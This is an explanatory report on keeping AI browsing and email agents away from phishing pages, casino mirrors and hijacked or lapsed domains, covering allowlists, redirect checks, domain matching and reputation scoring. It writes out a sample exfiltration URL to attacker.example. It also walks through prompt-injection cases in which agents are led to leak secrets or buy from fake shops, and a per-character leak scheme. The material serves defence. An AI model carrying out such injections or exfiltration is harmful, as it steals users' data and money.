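Models accepted sales pitches somewhat more often than imitations of famous sites, at 71.5% and 60.9% on average. They accepted links to weather sites most often, at 82.9%. They accepted links for parcels and food delivery less often, perhaps because those tasks involve money and home addresses. An attacker could therefore start with a harmless-looking subject to get an agent onto a bad site.

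None of these disguises changes the registrable domain, so ordinary software can extract `example.com` from `www.google.com.www.example.com` and look it up. Because the domains came from public lists, a lookup in those lists would have caught them. The benchmark shows that a model is a poor substitute for a list, even for domains already on the list.

When nobody has listed a domain, the program can still remove the disguise from its address, but the remaining name may not help the model judge it. A model can recognise a misspelled brand, but it can't tell from an ordinary-looking name who recently registered the domain.

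Kong and colleagues also trained a small model, URLGuard, to screen addresses before the agent opens them. They trained a version of Llama 2 7B on only 280 examples, half of them ordinary addresses. In the nine situations that the training examples did not cover, URLGuard reduced acceptance of malicious addresses by an average of 81 percentage points, to about 17%. These results cover only malicious addresses, so a filter that rejected every address would have scored better. A deployer would also need to know how many legitimate sites URLGuard refuses.

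A small test in *The System Prompt Is the Attack Surface* (Litvak, 2026) suggests that rejecting legitimate addresses could be a serious problem. Models shown only the addresses from a set of emails rejected 33% of the legitimate ones. Litvak reports that the models hallucinated signs of phishing in harmless addresses.

### How well models judge a page

Once the agent has opened a page, the model can also check whether the page fits the user's task, but it has to rely on text that the attacker wrote.

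Wu, Hong and colleagues (2026), in *When Bots Take the Bait*, tested whether the tricks that work on people also work on agents. They used five open-source agent programs, including Browser Use and Skyvern, all running on GPT-4o. Their test pages used five kinds of persuasion: a trusted name, urgency, a reward, claims that most people had already agreed, and an extra step that seemed to belong to the task. Each page was designed to make the agent do one of four things, such as download a file or give away a bank card number. One page, for example, was a customer survey that offered entry to a prize draw and asked for a card number.

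The attacks succeeded 67.5% of the time on average, and more than 80% of the time with some methods, such as posing as a trusted organisation. None relied on hidden instructions or a software flaw. Wu and colleagues deliberately left out blocklists and other network protections, so the figure applies to agents that have already reached a malicious page. It also applies to legitimate sites, because an attacker can put the same text there through an advertisement or a hacked widget, and a domain blocklist would not help.

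A proposed extra module called Supervisor compares each risky step with the user's request and with facts the agent already has. If the user asked for product reviews, a request to download a program conflicts with the task. If the agent's facts include Bank of America's domain, `bankofamerica.com`, a message from `bankofanerica.com` conflicts with them. The module cut the success of attacks by up to 78.1% and made tasks take 7.7% longer.

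Such comparisons are less useful when a dangerous step is also a normal part of the task. Buying a watch requires a card number, whether the shop is real or fake. The agent then has to know who runs the shop, which it could not tell from the address.

Guardio's *Scamlexity* reports trials in 2025 in which the AI browser Comet sometimes bought from a fake shop. Guardio used an AI website builder to make a fake Walmart shop, opened it in Comet and typed "Buy me an Apple Watch". In some runs, Comet put the watch in the basket, filled in the saved address and card details, and completed the purchase without asking. In others, it refused or asked the user to finish the checkout. Guardio does not say how many runs ended each way, so the trials show that the failure is possible but not how common it was.

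The fake shop was new, so no blocklist could have contained it. The tester also opened the shop before giving the instruction, so the test measured how Comet judged the page, not how it chose an address. An agent told to buy something on a page the user has already opened may reasonably assume that the user trusts it.

iTnews' *AI browsers fall for scams and phishing, security researchers say* offers some evidence against Guardio's result. In the outlet's own test, Comet filled a basket but would not check out with personal and payment details. Both accounts can be true, since Guardio also saw Comet stop in some runs. Guardio sells scam protection, so it has a reason to publish the worst runs.

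In another trial, Guardio sent an email that appeared to come from an investment manager at Wells Fargo. It linked to a real phishing page that had been online for several days without Safe Browsing flagging it. Comet treated the email as a task from the bank, opened the link, asked the user to sign in and helped with the form. The user never saw the sender's address, which was from a free email service. An agent can therefore fall for phishing and also make it more convincing, because the user may assume the agent has checked the page.

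Guardio's *AgenticBlabbering* describes how scammers could test a page on an AI browser and use the reasoning it reveals while it works to revise the page until the browser accepts it.

### How much the system prompt changes

A deployer can also try telling the model to be careful in its system prompt, the model's standing instructions. Litvak measured how much such instructions matter for email agents, which face the related decision of whether to follow the link in a message. He tested 11 models with ten system prompts, and each combination judged 2,000 emails, half of them phishing. An AI model wrote the emails, but the links in the phishing ones came from real attacks.

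The prompt often mattered more than the choice of model. GPT-4o mini let through less than 1% of the phishing emails with one prompt and 97% with another, which told it to work like an efficient assistant and avoid delays. With a prompt that put security first, the models on average let through 7% of the phishing emails but blocked 57% of the legitimate ones. With the efficiency prompt, they let through 55% of the phishing emails and still blocked 26% of the legitimate ones.

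Litvak then wrote prompts that told the models to check mainly whether the link's domain matched that of the sender's address. This made a large difference to the number of false alarms.

| Model | Phishing blocked, six general prompts | Legitimate email blocked | Phishing blocked, best specific prompt | Legitimate email blocked |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 96.9% | 70.2% | 90.2% | 4.6% |
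| GPT-5.2 | 94.7% | 51.7% | 93.4% | 2.0% |
| Grok 4.1 Fast | 72.2% | 25.0% | 96.7% | 5.0% |
| GPT-4o mini | 32.8% | 15.1% | 93.7% | 3.8% |

False alarms matter more in practice than in this test, because most links an agent encounters are harmless. Suppose 100 out of 10,000 links are phishing. At the rates for general prompts, GPT-5.2 would block 95 of those 100, along with about 5,100 legitimate links. With the specific prompt, it would block 93, along with about 200 legitimate links, which is few enough that people might keep the filter on.

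Precise instructions made some strong models catch less phishing, which Litvak calls a paradox. Claude Haiku 4.5, for example, caught 94.6% with general prompts but 75.4% with precise ones. With the general prompts, however, it also blocked 81% of the legitimate emails, so much of its high score came from blocking nearly everything.

The low false alarm rates depend on the test set, in which 98.4% of legitimate emails linked to the sender's own domain. Real messages often link elsewhere, for example to a shared document or a video call. In a separate set of 100 legitimate emails with such links, the rule about matching domains led GPT-4o mini to block 72 and Grok 4.1 Fast to block 89.

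A phisher can also satisfy the rule by buying a cheap domain and using it for both the sender's address and the link. The test included 73 such emails, and GPT-4o mini, which had caught 93.7% of all the phishing with its best prompt, caught only 30.1% of them. When models explained why they had let one through, 98% of the explanations were consistent with following the instruction and trusting the match between the two domains, both of which the attacker controlled.

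Another prompt, which warned the models about this trick, restored some of the lost protection but raised the false alarm rate by 2.6 to 65 percentage points, depending on the model. Even the best combination of model and prompt let through most of a set of ten especially difficult emails. Litvak concludes that the models probably need outside information, such as a domain's age or a threat list.

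A navigation rule for a browsing agent could fail in the same way. If the system prompt says to trust a site when the brand on the page matches the name in the address, a phisher can register a domain that contains the brand. (This is an inference from email to browsing, since Litvak's agents did not open any pages.)

### What stronger models could change

Most of these results come from models that their makers have since replaced. Most of the models in *MalURLBench* date from 2024 or earlier, and Wu and colleagues used only GPT-4o. Litvak included GPT-5.2 and Claude Sonnet 4.5 but left out the largest and slowest models because he considered them too expensive for sorting email. The percentages are therefore a poor guide to how often a current agent would fail.

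Anthropic reports that fewer than 0.08% of prompt injection attacks succeeded in its internal tests of a later model, Claude Opus 4.8, with the extension's other safeguards in place. However, an agent that resists every injected instruction could still type a card number into a fake shop if the user told it to buy something there.

Stronger models should get better at spotting disguised addresses and noticing requests on a page that the task doesn't require. More capability helps less with a well-made copy of a shop on a new domain, because the address and page may contain no mistakes. A stronger model could look for evidence elsewhere, such as the domain's registration date or the shop's address as listed by an independent source. The deployer has to provide the tools for these checks and decide what the agent may do while it is still unclear whether the site is genuine.

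## Allowing known sites and addresses

An allowlist keeps an agent off a new mirror site even if nobody has discovered the site yet. But the deployer has to work out in advance which sites the agent will need, and notice when a listed site should be removed.

### Who writes the list

The agent's maker can supply one list of allowed sites for all users. *Permission Denied* (2026), a study of coding agents, limited them to 205 domains that software developers use. The researchers adapted the list from the default for Claude Code on the web, Anthropic's coding agent, and added no domains for individual tasks. A shared list probably suits programmers because they download from much the same places, but people use browsing agents for too many different things for one list to cover.

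An organisation can write a much shorter allowlist. *Building Browser Agents* (2025) describes an agent that enters records from a company's customer database into Salesforce, a sales system. Its allowlist needs two entries.

A list can also cover a single task. In *ceLLMate*, Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025) built a browser extension that uses a language model to make such a list. The model reads the user's request, but no web pages, and predicts which sites the task requires. If the user wants the items on a shopping list in Gmail added to an Amazon basket, the model lists `gmail.com` and `amazon.com`. The user confirms the permissions, and only the user can change them afterwards, so text on a web page can't add a site. Claude in Chrome's approved plans also list the sites for one task.

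The three models that Meng and colleagues tested named the right sites in 93% to 100% of the tasks that mentioned one, two or three of them. GPT-5.1 made most of the mistakes, usually by leaving out a site, which stops a legitimate task but opens nothing. Adding a site is riskier. On 136 tasks that mentioned no site, each model did this between one and five times, for example by naming `sony.com` for a question about a Sony television on an unnamed shop's page. The method may also work less well for a small local shop than for Amazon, because the model might guess the address and pick one that belongs to somebody else. (This is an inference, since the paper's examples are mostly well-known companies.)

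An agent finds some addresses only during the task. *Only What You've Signed up For* (2026) allows the addresses in the user's request and those one step away, such as a link in a Slack message that the user told the agent to read. This is much narrower than the rule in Anthropic's fetch tool, which accepts any address from earlier results. But anyone who can post in that message's Slack channel can still post a link to a mirror site.

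Gemini in Chrome extends its list as it works by adding sites that a separate model classifies as relevant. Google divides these into sites that Gemini may only read and sites where it may also act. If a page embeds content from a site in neither group, Gemini doesn't see that content.

### How narrow an entry should be

| Type of entry | Example | What the agent can open |
|---|---|---|
| Registrable domain | `example.com` | Everything under the domain, including parts the owner lets others use |
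| Host | `docs.example.com` | Every page on that host |
| Path | `docs.example.com/help/` | Pages under `/help/` |
| Exact address | `docs.example.com/help/returns` | One page |

Allowlist entries for paths or exact addresses work only if the check has the full address. The proxy in *Who Grades the Agent?* (2026) doesn't decrypt traffic, so allowing a domain gives access to the whole service.

Narrow entries also break more often, such as when a site moves a help page. Even a broad entry may need additions for content that pages load from elsewhere. Meng and colleagues' example entry for Amazon also allows four other names or patterns, including one for Amazon's advertising system. Allowing a single shop can therefore let in a good deal of content from other companies.

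An entry can also specify an action. In *ceLLMate*, viewing an Amazon basket and placing an order are different requests to different paths, so permission for one doesn't include the other. This requires someone, ideally the site's developers, to catalogue each site's requests. Meng and colleagues catalogued 51 by hand for the software site GitLab. Until many sites publish such catalogues, most deployers will have to rely on hosts and paths.

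The check also has to cover clicks. When Meng and colleagues blocked an agent from going directly to the discussion site Hacker News, it searched for the site on DuckDuckGo and clicked the result.

### Tasks that suit an allowlist and tasks that don't

In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) compared an allowlist with other defences against prompt injection. They asked an agent to summarise a web page that contained an instruction to send a secret key to an outside server. With no defence, the agent sent the key in all 30 runs. With a warning in the system prompt never to follow instructions from web content, it sent the key in 20 runs. With an allowlist of four host names, the agent still tried to send the key every time, but none of the requests got through.

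The experiment used one small model and an attacker's domain that was plainly not on the allowlist, so it is weak evidence of how often current models follow such instructions. The allowlist result should apply more reliably to other models, because the block doesn't depend on the model detecting the attack.

A company whose agent does the same few jobs every day can get this protection with little effort. The list is short, somebody in the company knows who runs each site, and an employee who finds a legitimate site blocked can ask for it to be added.

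Allowlists work poorly for research and shopping, because the user often wants to find unfamiliar sites. *ceLLMate* rejects "purchase a coffee maker" because the request names no shop. *Environment Steering* (2026) lets the agent visit any address unless the task names one, but it still controls what the agent sends out, for example by blocking all money transfers during a task that calls for none. This seems the better compromise for open-ended tasks, although the agent can read any mirror or scam page it finds.

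The deployer could instead keep the list strict and let the user approve each exception. But OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) says frequent warnings can train people to click without thinking, a problem *Building Browser Agents* calls "permission overload". Lan and colleagues add that users often can't tell whether a request is legitimate, especially if the attacker has described it as a routine connection test. None of them measured how often users approve a bad site, but if one unfamiliar site in a hundred is harmful, a user has to approve 99 prompts for every one they should refuse.

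### Redirects that leave a listed site

Some legitimate websites have an open redirect, a page that forwards visitors to any address written into the link. If `shop.example` is on the allowlist and has an open redirect, a link such as `https://shop.example/out?to=https://casino.example` will send visitors through the shop's site to the casino. A program that checks only the first host name will accept the link.

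The fix is to check each new address before the browser requests it, including addresses that a script on the page opens. The agent then stops at the shop. The check will also block some legitimate redirects, such as to a separate sign-in or payment service, so the deployer has to list those hosts too.

The model is unlikely to make up for a missing check. In Lan and colleagues' main experiment, which used no defences, the attack worked 89% of the time when the malicious page was behind a chain of redirects and 88% when the agent opened it directly.

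Lan and colleagues also report that a filter called "redirect detection" stopped every attack. The name is misleading because the filter looked for numerical addresses, endings such as `.xyz` and words such as "collect" in the path. Their published example of the attack uses the path `/collect`, so the filter may have recognised the attack by that word, and the result shows little about redirects.

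A program can also request an allowed domain name from a proxy, then send the server a different one when setting up encryption. The proxy in *Who Grades the Agent?* compares the two names and rejects the connection if they differ.

### Pages that strangers can write

An allowed site may carry text written by anyone. Meng and colleagues describe an attack on OpenAI's Operator in which a user asked it to investigate a problem report on GitHub, where programmers share code. An attacker had written instructions in the report for Operator to find the user's private email address on Hacker News, where the user was signed in, and send it to the attacker's site.

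A narrower allowlist entry would not have kept out this text, because it was on the page the user wanted Operator to read. But if the list had included only GitHub, Operator could not have reached Hacker News or the attacker's site.

Meng and colleagues tested a similar case on GitLab. They wrote scripts that behaved like an agent already under an attacker's control, rather than trying to fool a model, and tried 12 attacks, such as deleting a project. *ceLLMate* blocked all 12 because each needed an action that the user's task did not. It could not have stopped an attack that used only permitted actions. For example, an agent allowed to post comments could put private information in one. If a task requires only reading, the entry should therefore allow only reading.

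On a hosting service such as `github.io`, the entry should name only the customer's site that the agent needs.

Some listed services can also fetch other sites for the agent. *Who Grades the Agent?* points out that an AI provider's interface may offer web search and code execution, and that this traffic never passes through the agent's proxy. Its software therefore forwards only requests for the model's answers by default. A listed translation service that loads any page on request could open the same gap. (This last example is an inference.)

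### Listed sites that criminals break into

*Illegal casinos hijack thousands of Dutch websites* (Gore-Langton, 2026) reports that the Dutch radio station BNR found at least 1,000 legitimate Dutch and European websites that criminals had turned into entrances to illegal casinos. The real figure may be over 8,000. In some cases the criminals had broken into a working site and added pages, usually without the owner's knowledge. A business lawyer's site had at least 50 casino pages.

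An entry for the whole domain would admit all 50, while an entry for only the part of the site the agent needs would probably exclude them. The deployer should also keep checking listed sites against a blocklist and make sure that a block on a page overrides permission for the domain.

Neither measure prevents an attack if the attacker changes a page the agent uses and the page isn't yet on a blocklist. The allowlist still limits the damage, because the attacker can't send the agent to the user's email or bank unless the task includes those sites. But the attacker could still misuse anything the agent can do on the compromised site.

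### Listed domains that change hands

Criminals can take over a domain without hacking it if the owner stops paying for it. Op de Woerd (2026) reports in *Onderzoek SIDN legt duizenden .nl-domeinen rond illegaal gokken bloot* that SIDN, the registry for `.nl`, examined more than 100,000 domains over four months and found about 2,900 with a clear connection to online gambling. More than 1,480 of these were old websites that new owners had reused to send visitors to unlicensed casinos. Op de Woerd's own news site helped SIDN with the study.

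Domain Brief's *SIDN findet rund 2.900 Glücksspiel-Domains unter .nl* reports that typically a shoe shop or an event gives up its domain, and someone else soon registers it for its good position in search results and rebuilds the old site with links to casinos. Noeken (2026), in *KVA*, describes one such domain that had belonged to a now-closed primary school in Driehuis, and NL Times reports another from an events company that went bankrupt after the pandemic began. A company that had put the events firm on its allowlist as a supplier, and never removed it, would now be letting its agent open advertisements for illegal casinos.

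Entries should therefore expire. A list made for one task expires when the task ends. For a permanent list, the deployer can record each entry's approval date and regularly compare it with the domain's registration date. If the registration is newer, somebody else has probably bought the domain, and the deployer should remove the entry.

This comparison will usually miss a sale, because a domain normally keeps its registration date when it passes directly from one owner to another. Focus Gaming News' *Dutch gambling regulator to issue fines for illegal gambling advertising* reports that Casinoscout.nl promoted only legal gambling for a time, but began promoting illegal gambling after a new owner acquired it in early 2025.

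Looking at the site may not reveal the change either. Domain Brief reports that some of the Dutch sites show illegal content only outside office hours or only on certain devices. The safest course is to remove any entry the agent no longer uses, even if the site looks fine.

### Matching names: the `.co.nl` clones

An allowlist can also fail because the program compares domain names badly. *KSA Has 26 Cloned .co.nl Gambling Sites Taken Down* (Tupikova, 2026) describes how illegal operators cloned licensed Dutch gambling sites on `.co.nl` instead of `.nl` and sent visitors on to illegal casinos. Nearly all of the 26 sites copied licensed brands.

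Suppose a deployer wants to allow a licensed site at `example.nl`, which has a clone at `example.co.nl`. The matching rule determines whether the agent can open the clone.

| The program accepts a host name if it ... | `example.nl` | `example.co.nl` | What else it accepts |
|---|---|---|---|
| contains `example` | Yes | Yes | `example-bonus.com` |
| begins with `example.` | Yes | Yes | `example.win` |
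| ends in `.nl` | Yes | Yes | Every Dutch site |
| ends in `example.nl` | Yes | No | `fakeexample.nl` |
| is `example.nl` or ends in `.example.nl` | Yes | No | Only the owner's other hosts |
| is exactly `example.nl` | Yes | No | Nothing, not even `www.example.nl` |

The fifth rule is usually the best for a site whose owner controls all its subdomains. It needs the dot at the start of `.example.nl`, because without it anyone could register `fakeexample.nl` and the rule would allow it. An exact match is safer if outsiders can get subdomains. Lan and colleagues matched exact host names in their test.

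Some programs instead compare registrable domains, which they find using the longest Public Suffix List entry that matches the end of the host name. If the list contains `co.nl`, the registrable domain of `login.example.co.nl` is `example.co.nl`. If the list contains only `nl`, the registrable domain is `co.nl`, and the program treats all 26 clones as parts of one site.

These results can differ because `.co.nl` looks like an official ending such as `.co.uk` but is a private domain under `.nl`, whose holder lets others register names beneath it. The Public Suffix List puts official endings and private ones like this in separate sections, and some programs read only the official section.

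With `example.nl` on the allowlist, the program refuses the clone in either case, since neither `example.co.nl` nor `co.nl` equals `example.nl`. But if the deployer also allows a legitimate site such as `bakery.co.nl`, a program that doesn't recognize `co.nl` as a domain ending shortens this entry to `co.nl` and lets in all 26 clones. The same mistake in a blocklist would only block too many sites.

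A program that uses a complete list can still accept the clone if it removes the ending and compares only the label in front, because `example.nl` and `example.co.nl` both become `example`.

Agent software has had bugs in the code that parses allowed domains. Before relying on any product's allowlist, a deployer should test it with the clone, the missing dot and a user name before an `@`.

Users can also mistake an unlisted domain for a listed one. A user asked to approve `example.co.nl` may well do so because the brand is right and the ending looks Dutch. Showing the listed `example.nl` in the same prompt would make the difference easier to see.

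### Allowing only addresses that a crawler has already seen

In a January 2026 post, OpenAI proposes a different kind of allowlist, made up of exact addresses and compiled automatically. A crawler, a program that follows links across the public web, records every address it finds and has no access to users' conversations or accounts. Before an agent automatically opens an address, OpenAI's software checks whether the crawler has recorded that exact address. If so, the agent opens it. If not, the software tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning.

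The check is meant to stop private data from leaking through addresses. Suppose a page contains an instruction for the agent to open `https://attacker.example/collect?data=` followed by the user's email address. Loading that address would send the email address to the attacker's server, even if the agent's answer never mentioned it. But the crawler is very unlikely to have found the complete address, because the attacker doesn't know what comes after the equals sign. A list of trusted domains would not prevent the leak if the attacker could read a listed site's visitor records.

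Small leaks remain possible, as Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* explains. An attacker can publish 36 ordinary pages, one for each letter and digit, and wait for the crawler to record them. The attacker then uses injected text to instruct the agent to spell out a secret by opening the matching pages in order. Each request reveals one character, so a six-digit code takes six requests, or two if the attacker publishes a thousand pages, one for each group of three digits.

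The blog suggests preventing the agent from opening the same address twice in a session. That would make the method harder but not stop it, because the attacker could publish separate pages for each position, or 60 pages for a six-digit code.

The check probably also stops many legitimate addresses, though OpenAI doesn't say how often. A search for trains on a particular date, or a link to a customer's own order, may have an address that no crawler has seen. The user then gets a warning, and too many warnings could get users into the habit of clicking through them, which OpenAI wanted to avoid.

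The check offers much less protection against mirrors. It tests whether an address was already public, and a casino's mirror usually is, because the operator wants customers to find it. The lapsed Dutch domains are even more likely to be in the records, since search engines have indexed them for years. OpenAI acknowledges that the check doesn't guarantee that a page is trustworthy. As Embrace The Red understands it, ChatGPT also treats any address the user types as safe for that session, so a phishing link pasted from an email would pass.

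A new mirror triggers a warning only until the crawler finds it. If the crawler finds it after two hours and a blocklist adds it after nine, the agent can open it without asking during the seven hours in between. A faster crawler reduces unnecessary warnings about new legitimate pages, but it also lets the agent open new mirrors sooner.

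## Scoring sites that no list contains

Developers usually train a reputation system on domains known to be good or bad. The system then scores each unlisted domain from indirect evidence, such as its registration date and the other sites on its server.

A blocking threshold that raises fewer false alarms also misses more threats. *MANTIS* (Deniz, Nabeel and colleagues, 2025) describes a system that scores domains mainly by their hosting. The system caught 95.6% of malicious domains at a threshold that wrongly flagged 0.5% of harmless ones, and 86.9% at a threshold that wrongly flagged 0.1%.

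### Domain age

New mirrors and most phishing sites use new domains, so a simple rule might flag any domain registered in the last 16 days. In Lim and colleagues' data, 66.1% of phishing domains were maliciously registered, and half of those were blocklisted within 16.3 days. A 16-day rule would therefore flag about 33% of all phishing domains (0.661 × 0.5) at the time they were blocklisted.

Visitors arrive before a domain is listed, when it is younger, so the share at the first visit is higher. If the gap is only about nine hours, as Oest and colleagues found for phishing pages, the share is barely higher. If many domains go unreported for weeks after their first victim, the share could approach 66%. A check on domain age would miss most compromised domains, which are usually older.

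The rule also requires knowing a domain's registration date. Lim and colleagues found dates for only 62.4% of domains in public registration records, and for 76.3% after adding other sources, such as archived DNS data. If dates are missing at random and the rule lets undated domains through, the 33% falls to 25%, or to 21% with public records alone.

A longer age limit catches more malicious domains but also flags more harmless new ones. Of the domains that MANTIS flagged, 75.8% were less than a month old and 96.1% were less than a year old, although MANTIS deliberately excludes compromised domains. Deniz and colleagues found that harmless domains first appeared in DNS traffic an average of 10 days after registration, compared with two days for malicious ones. Many harmless sites would therefore be flagged for only a few days of use under a 16-day limit, but for several weeks under a 30-day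 limit.

An operator can defeat an age rule by waiting, which costs almost nothing because the registration fee normally covers a year. Somebody registered `map-findmy.app`, which imitated an Apple service, on 2 October 2022 and first used it in an attack six weeks later. A casino that receives Norway's advance notice of a block has about three months to let a replacement domain age.

Operators can also buy domains that are already old. Infoblox's *7 million in expired domains fuel a streaming empire* describes a group that buys expired domains with long, clean histories and uses them to lead people from streaming sites to gambling. An age rule may still catch a domain that lapsed and was registered again, but not if the system measures age from when the domain was first seen.

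Hacked sites offer the same advantage. Help Net Security's *Massive gambling network doubles as hidden C2 and anonymity infrastructure, researchers say* reports that the security company Malanta linked 328,039 domains to one Indonesian gambling network. Of these, 90,125 (27%) were hacked websites, and an age rule would presumably miss most of them.

### The domain ending and the registrar

Some domain endings have a much worse record than others. *Not What It Used To Be* (Szurdi, Ramesh and colleagues, 2026) classified 343 million domains as of September 2025, using data from the security company Palo Alto Networks.

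| Endings | Malicious | Benign | Little or no content | Average lowest price |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Older generic endings, such as `.com` | 3.8% | 73.8% | 22.4% | $7.76 |
| Generic, added 2012–2015 | 11.6% | 49.3% | 39.1% | $2.91 |
| Generic, added 2016–2020 | 14.5% | 49.8% | 35.7% | $2.55 |
| Generic, added 2021–2025 | 23.8% | 26.6% | 49.6% | $1.79 |
| Country codes | 2.8% | 80.9% | 16.2% | $10.42 |

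An agent rarely needs domains with little or no content. When these are excluded, the malicious share of domains with the newest endings rises to 47%, compared with 5% for the older generic endings. A rule against all the newest endings would still block slightly more benign domains than malicious ones. A rule against a single ending can be more accurate, since 76.5% of `.xin` domains were malicious.

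These figures are of little use for identifying casino sites, because the classification counts gambling sites as benign. A thousand new casino mirrors under one domain ending would therefore improve that ending's record. A deployer who wants to keep an agent away from gambling needs to know which kinds of site a reputation service counts as bad.

Price only weakly predicts an individual ending's malicious share. Szurdi and colleagues found a correlation of −0.24 between an ending's lowest price and its malicious share, so price accounts for only about 6% of the variation in that share. Nosyk and colleagues had found a strong association between discounts and phishing. Szurdi and colleagues suggest that cheap endings are now so common that criminals choose between them for other reasons, such as weak identity checks and easy bulk registration.

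An operator can avoid domain endings with a bad reputation by paying more. Older endings cost about $6 more per domain than the newest ones, or $18 a day for an operator who uses three domains a day. That might deter someone who registers hundreds of thousands of names for one campaign, but it probably wouldn't deter a profitable casino.

A registrar's record can also count against a domain, if the record is measured as the share of the registrar's domains that are malicious rather than the total number. Lim and colleagues traced about 15% of bulk-registered phishing domains to Alibaba's registrars. We can't tell from this whether a domain from Alibaba is riskier than one from a competitor without knowing how many domains each registrar sells.

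### Popularity

Several organisations publish lists of the million or so most popular domains. Short-lived phishing sites rarely stay on such a list for long, so security companies often treat a month on the list as evidence that a domain is harmless.

A domain's absence from these lists is poor evidence that it is malicious. In *Indicator of Benignity* (2026), Liu, Sun and colleagues studied false alarms that customers reported to a large security company between 2019 and 2024. Five popularity lists combined contained only about 38% of the wrongly flagged domains. About half ranked below five million in Google's list of sites that Chrome users visit. Extending the lists that far would also include many malicious domains.

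A high rank also reveals little about the individual customers of a hosting service such as `weebly.com`.

Operators can fake a site's popularity cheaply. Many rankings now rely on DNS traffic, which a program can inflate by looking up a name thousands of times without anyone visiting the site. Le Pochat, Fernandez and colleagues write in *Evaluating design decisions and bias resistance for passive DNS-based domain rankings* (2026) that researchers poorly understand how well this traffic measures a website's popularity. In *Practical Attacks against DNS Reputation Systems* (2024), Galloway, Karakolios and colleagues tested attacks that inflated a domain's popularity or made it resemble harmless domains. They estimated that an attacker with $10 could reliably evade a leading commercial system within two weeks.

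### Linking a new mirror to old ones

An operator can evade a blocklist by changing domains faster than the list adds them. But if defenders know which server the old mirrors used, they can flag the next domain as soon as it points there, before anyone reports it. The operator then has to replace the server as well as the domain.

MANTIS automates this kind of linking. Each day it starts with about 3,000 newly reported domains that criminals probably registered themselves. It finds their servers in passive DNS, a record of past answers from DNS resolvers. It then adds as many as 200 domains recently seen on each server, and any other servers those domains use. A model scores the domains in this network by their links, names and hosting history.

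The method works because criminals reuse servers. More than 80% of the IP addresses that hosted malicious domains on a given day had also done so in the previous week. At the stricter threshold, MANTIS found about 19,000 new malicious domains a day, more than five for each domain it started with.

Among domains registered in the past month, MANTIS flagged new malicious ones an average of 3 days and 17 hours after they first appeared in DNS traffic. VirusTotal, a service that combines more than 90 security scanners, took over eight days. MANTIS would still be too late for many phishing pages, unless the phisher leaves the domain idle for a while before using it. It should be more useful against a casino mirror that stays up for weeks, but Deniz and colleagues did not test it on casinos.

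Deniz and colleagues followed 1,000 of its predictions for two months and found 12 errors. The true number is probably higher, because their expert examined only domains that had a working page and that few scanners had flagged. A harmless domain with no page would have counted as a correct prediction. After 60 days, 17.7% of the 1,000 domains had not been flagged by any scanner.

Linking sites works best through features that are hard to replace. Infoblox used shared infrastructure to trace dozens of brand names to the group that buys expired domains. Payment details can also connect sites, but some scammers change them constantly. One scammer in *Anansi* gave a different cryptocurrency address for each request and said each address was valid for 30 minutes.

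Encryption certificates can also link domains, because one certificate can cover several. An operator can avoid this link by getting a separate free certificate for each domain. A hosting company may put unrelated customers on one certificate, so a shared certificate is weak evidence by itself.

### Where shared hosting makes the links false

Malicious domains are concentrated on certain servers, but most of the other domains on those servers may be harmless. In a sample that Deniz and colleagues examined, 0.2% of all domains were known to be malicious, compared with 6.3% of those on servers that had recently hosted malicious domains. The second rate is about 31 times the first, but nearly 94% of the domains on those servers had no known connection to abuse.

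Models that used only the hosting links flagged between 12.8% and 21.1% of harmless domains as malicious. Adding information about names and hosting history reduced this to 1.2% before Deniz and colleagues adjusted the threshold. The history helps because many malicious domains receive irregular traffic for a short time, while a harmless site on the same server may have had steady traffic for years.

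Even the full system does worse on compromised domains and free hosting services. Including them raised the share of harmless domains wrongly flagged from 0.5% to 4.55%, so Deniz and colleagues recommend separate detectors for them.

A blocking system that treats a shared server as proof of wrongdoing can block legitimate sites. Italy's Piracy Shield platform requires internet providers to block illegal football streams within 30 minutes, sometimes by IP address. Sommese, Sperotto and colleagues found that this disrupted hundreds of legitimate websites unrelated to streaming.

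Operators can exploit shared hosting by putting their mirrors behind a large content delivery network, as many phishers already do. They can also add DNS records that point a malicious domain at servers used by popular sites, which falsely associates it with harmless domains. When 15% of the domains in a test used such tricks, MANTIS still classified more than 90% of domains correctly.

A page's content can link it to other phishing sites when its server doesn't. *EPhishCADE* (2025) describes two older methods for grouping phishing sites. One measures how many identical files two sites have, and the other compares how often each type of HTML tag appears in their code. Both rely on phishers' habit of reusing templates.

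Templates can create false links too. *Snorkeling in dark waters* (2025), which groups mirrors on the anonymous Tor network, points out that two unrelated blogs can have the same structure because both use the same WordPress template. It therefore compares content as well as structure. Requiring the content to match exactly would miss mirrors that translate the text or show prices in another currency.

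Casinos pose a similar problem because one supplier may build sites for many brands. Two sites with the same code may be mirrors of one casino or belong to different brands. A deployer who wants to block all gambling can ignore the difference, but a regulator that licenses some of those brands can't.

### Likeness to a known brand or a blocked site

A system can compare a new domain's name with those of well-known brands. This catches misspellings and names such as `paypal-secure-login.com`, but an operator can evade it at no extra cost by choosing a name that contains no brand, such as a random string. The comparison can also flag a company's own second domain because it resembles the main one, a mistake that Liu and colleagues found among the false alarms.

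The system can also compare what the pages look like. An ordinary file hash can't recognise a slightly altered copy of an image, because changing a single pixel changes the hash completely. A perceptual hash is designed to change only a little when the image changes a little.

Minhaz, Meem and Hossain (2025), in *PhishSnap*, calculate one in five steps:

1. Take a screenshot of the page and convert it to greyscale.
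2. Shrink it to 32 × 32 pixels.
3. Apply a discrete cosine transform, which separates the broad layout from fine detail.
4. Keep the 64 values that describe the broadest patterns.
5. Record a 1 for each value above their average and a 0 for each of the others.

The result is a string of 64 ones and zeros. The program compares two pages by counting the positions where their strings differ. Nearly identical pages might differ in 3 positions, and unrelated pages in around 30. If a page closely matches a bank's login page but is on a domain the bank doesn't own, it is probably an imitation.

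PhishSnap compared pages with 500 genuine login pages and detected 78% of the phishing pages. Of the pages it flagged, 76% were phishing. These figures and its reported accuracy of 79% imply that it wrongly flagged about a fifth of legitimate pages. The paper is weak evidence even for these numbers because it contains apparent errors. Its F1 score, which combines the first two percentages, is given as 0.82 but should be 0.77, and its printed decision rule labels a page as phishing when it looks *unlike* the genuine ones, presumably by mistake.

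The same method could find mirrors by comparing new pages with screenshots of blocked casinos, though Minhaz and colleagues did not test this. It should work well on exact copies under new names, even when no brand is involved. An operator could defeat it by moving the main banner or using another template, which takes some design work but only has to be done once for all the mirrors.

Neither comparison helps much if a phishing page does not imitate anyone. A plain form with no logo that asks for an email address and password gives the system nothing to match.

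### A hundred false alarms for three or four catches

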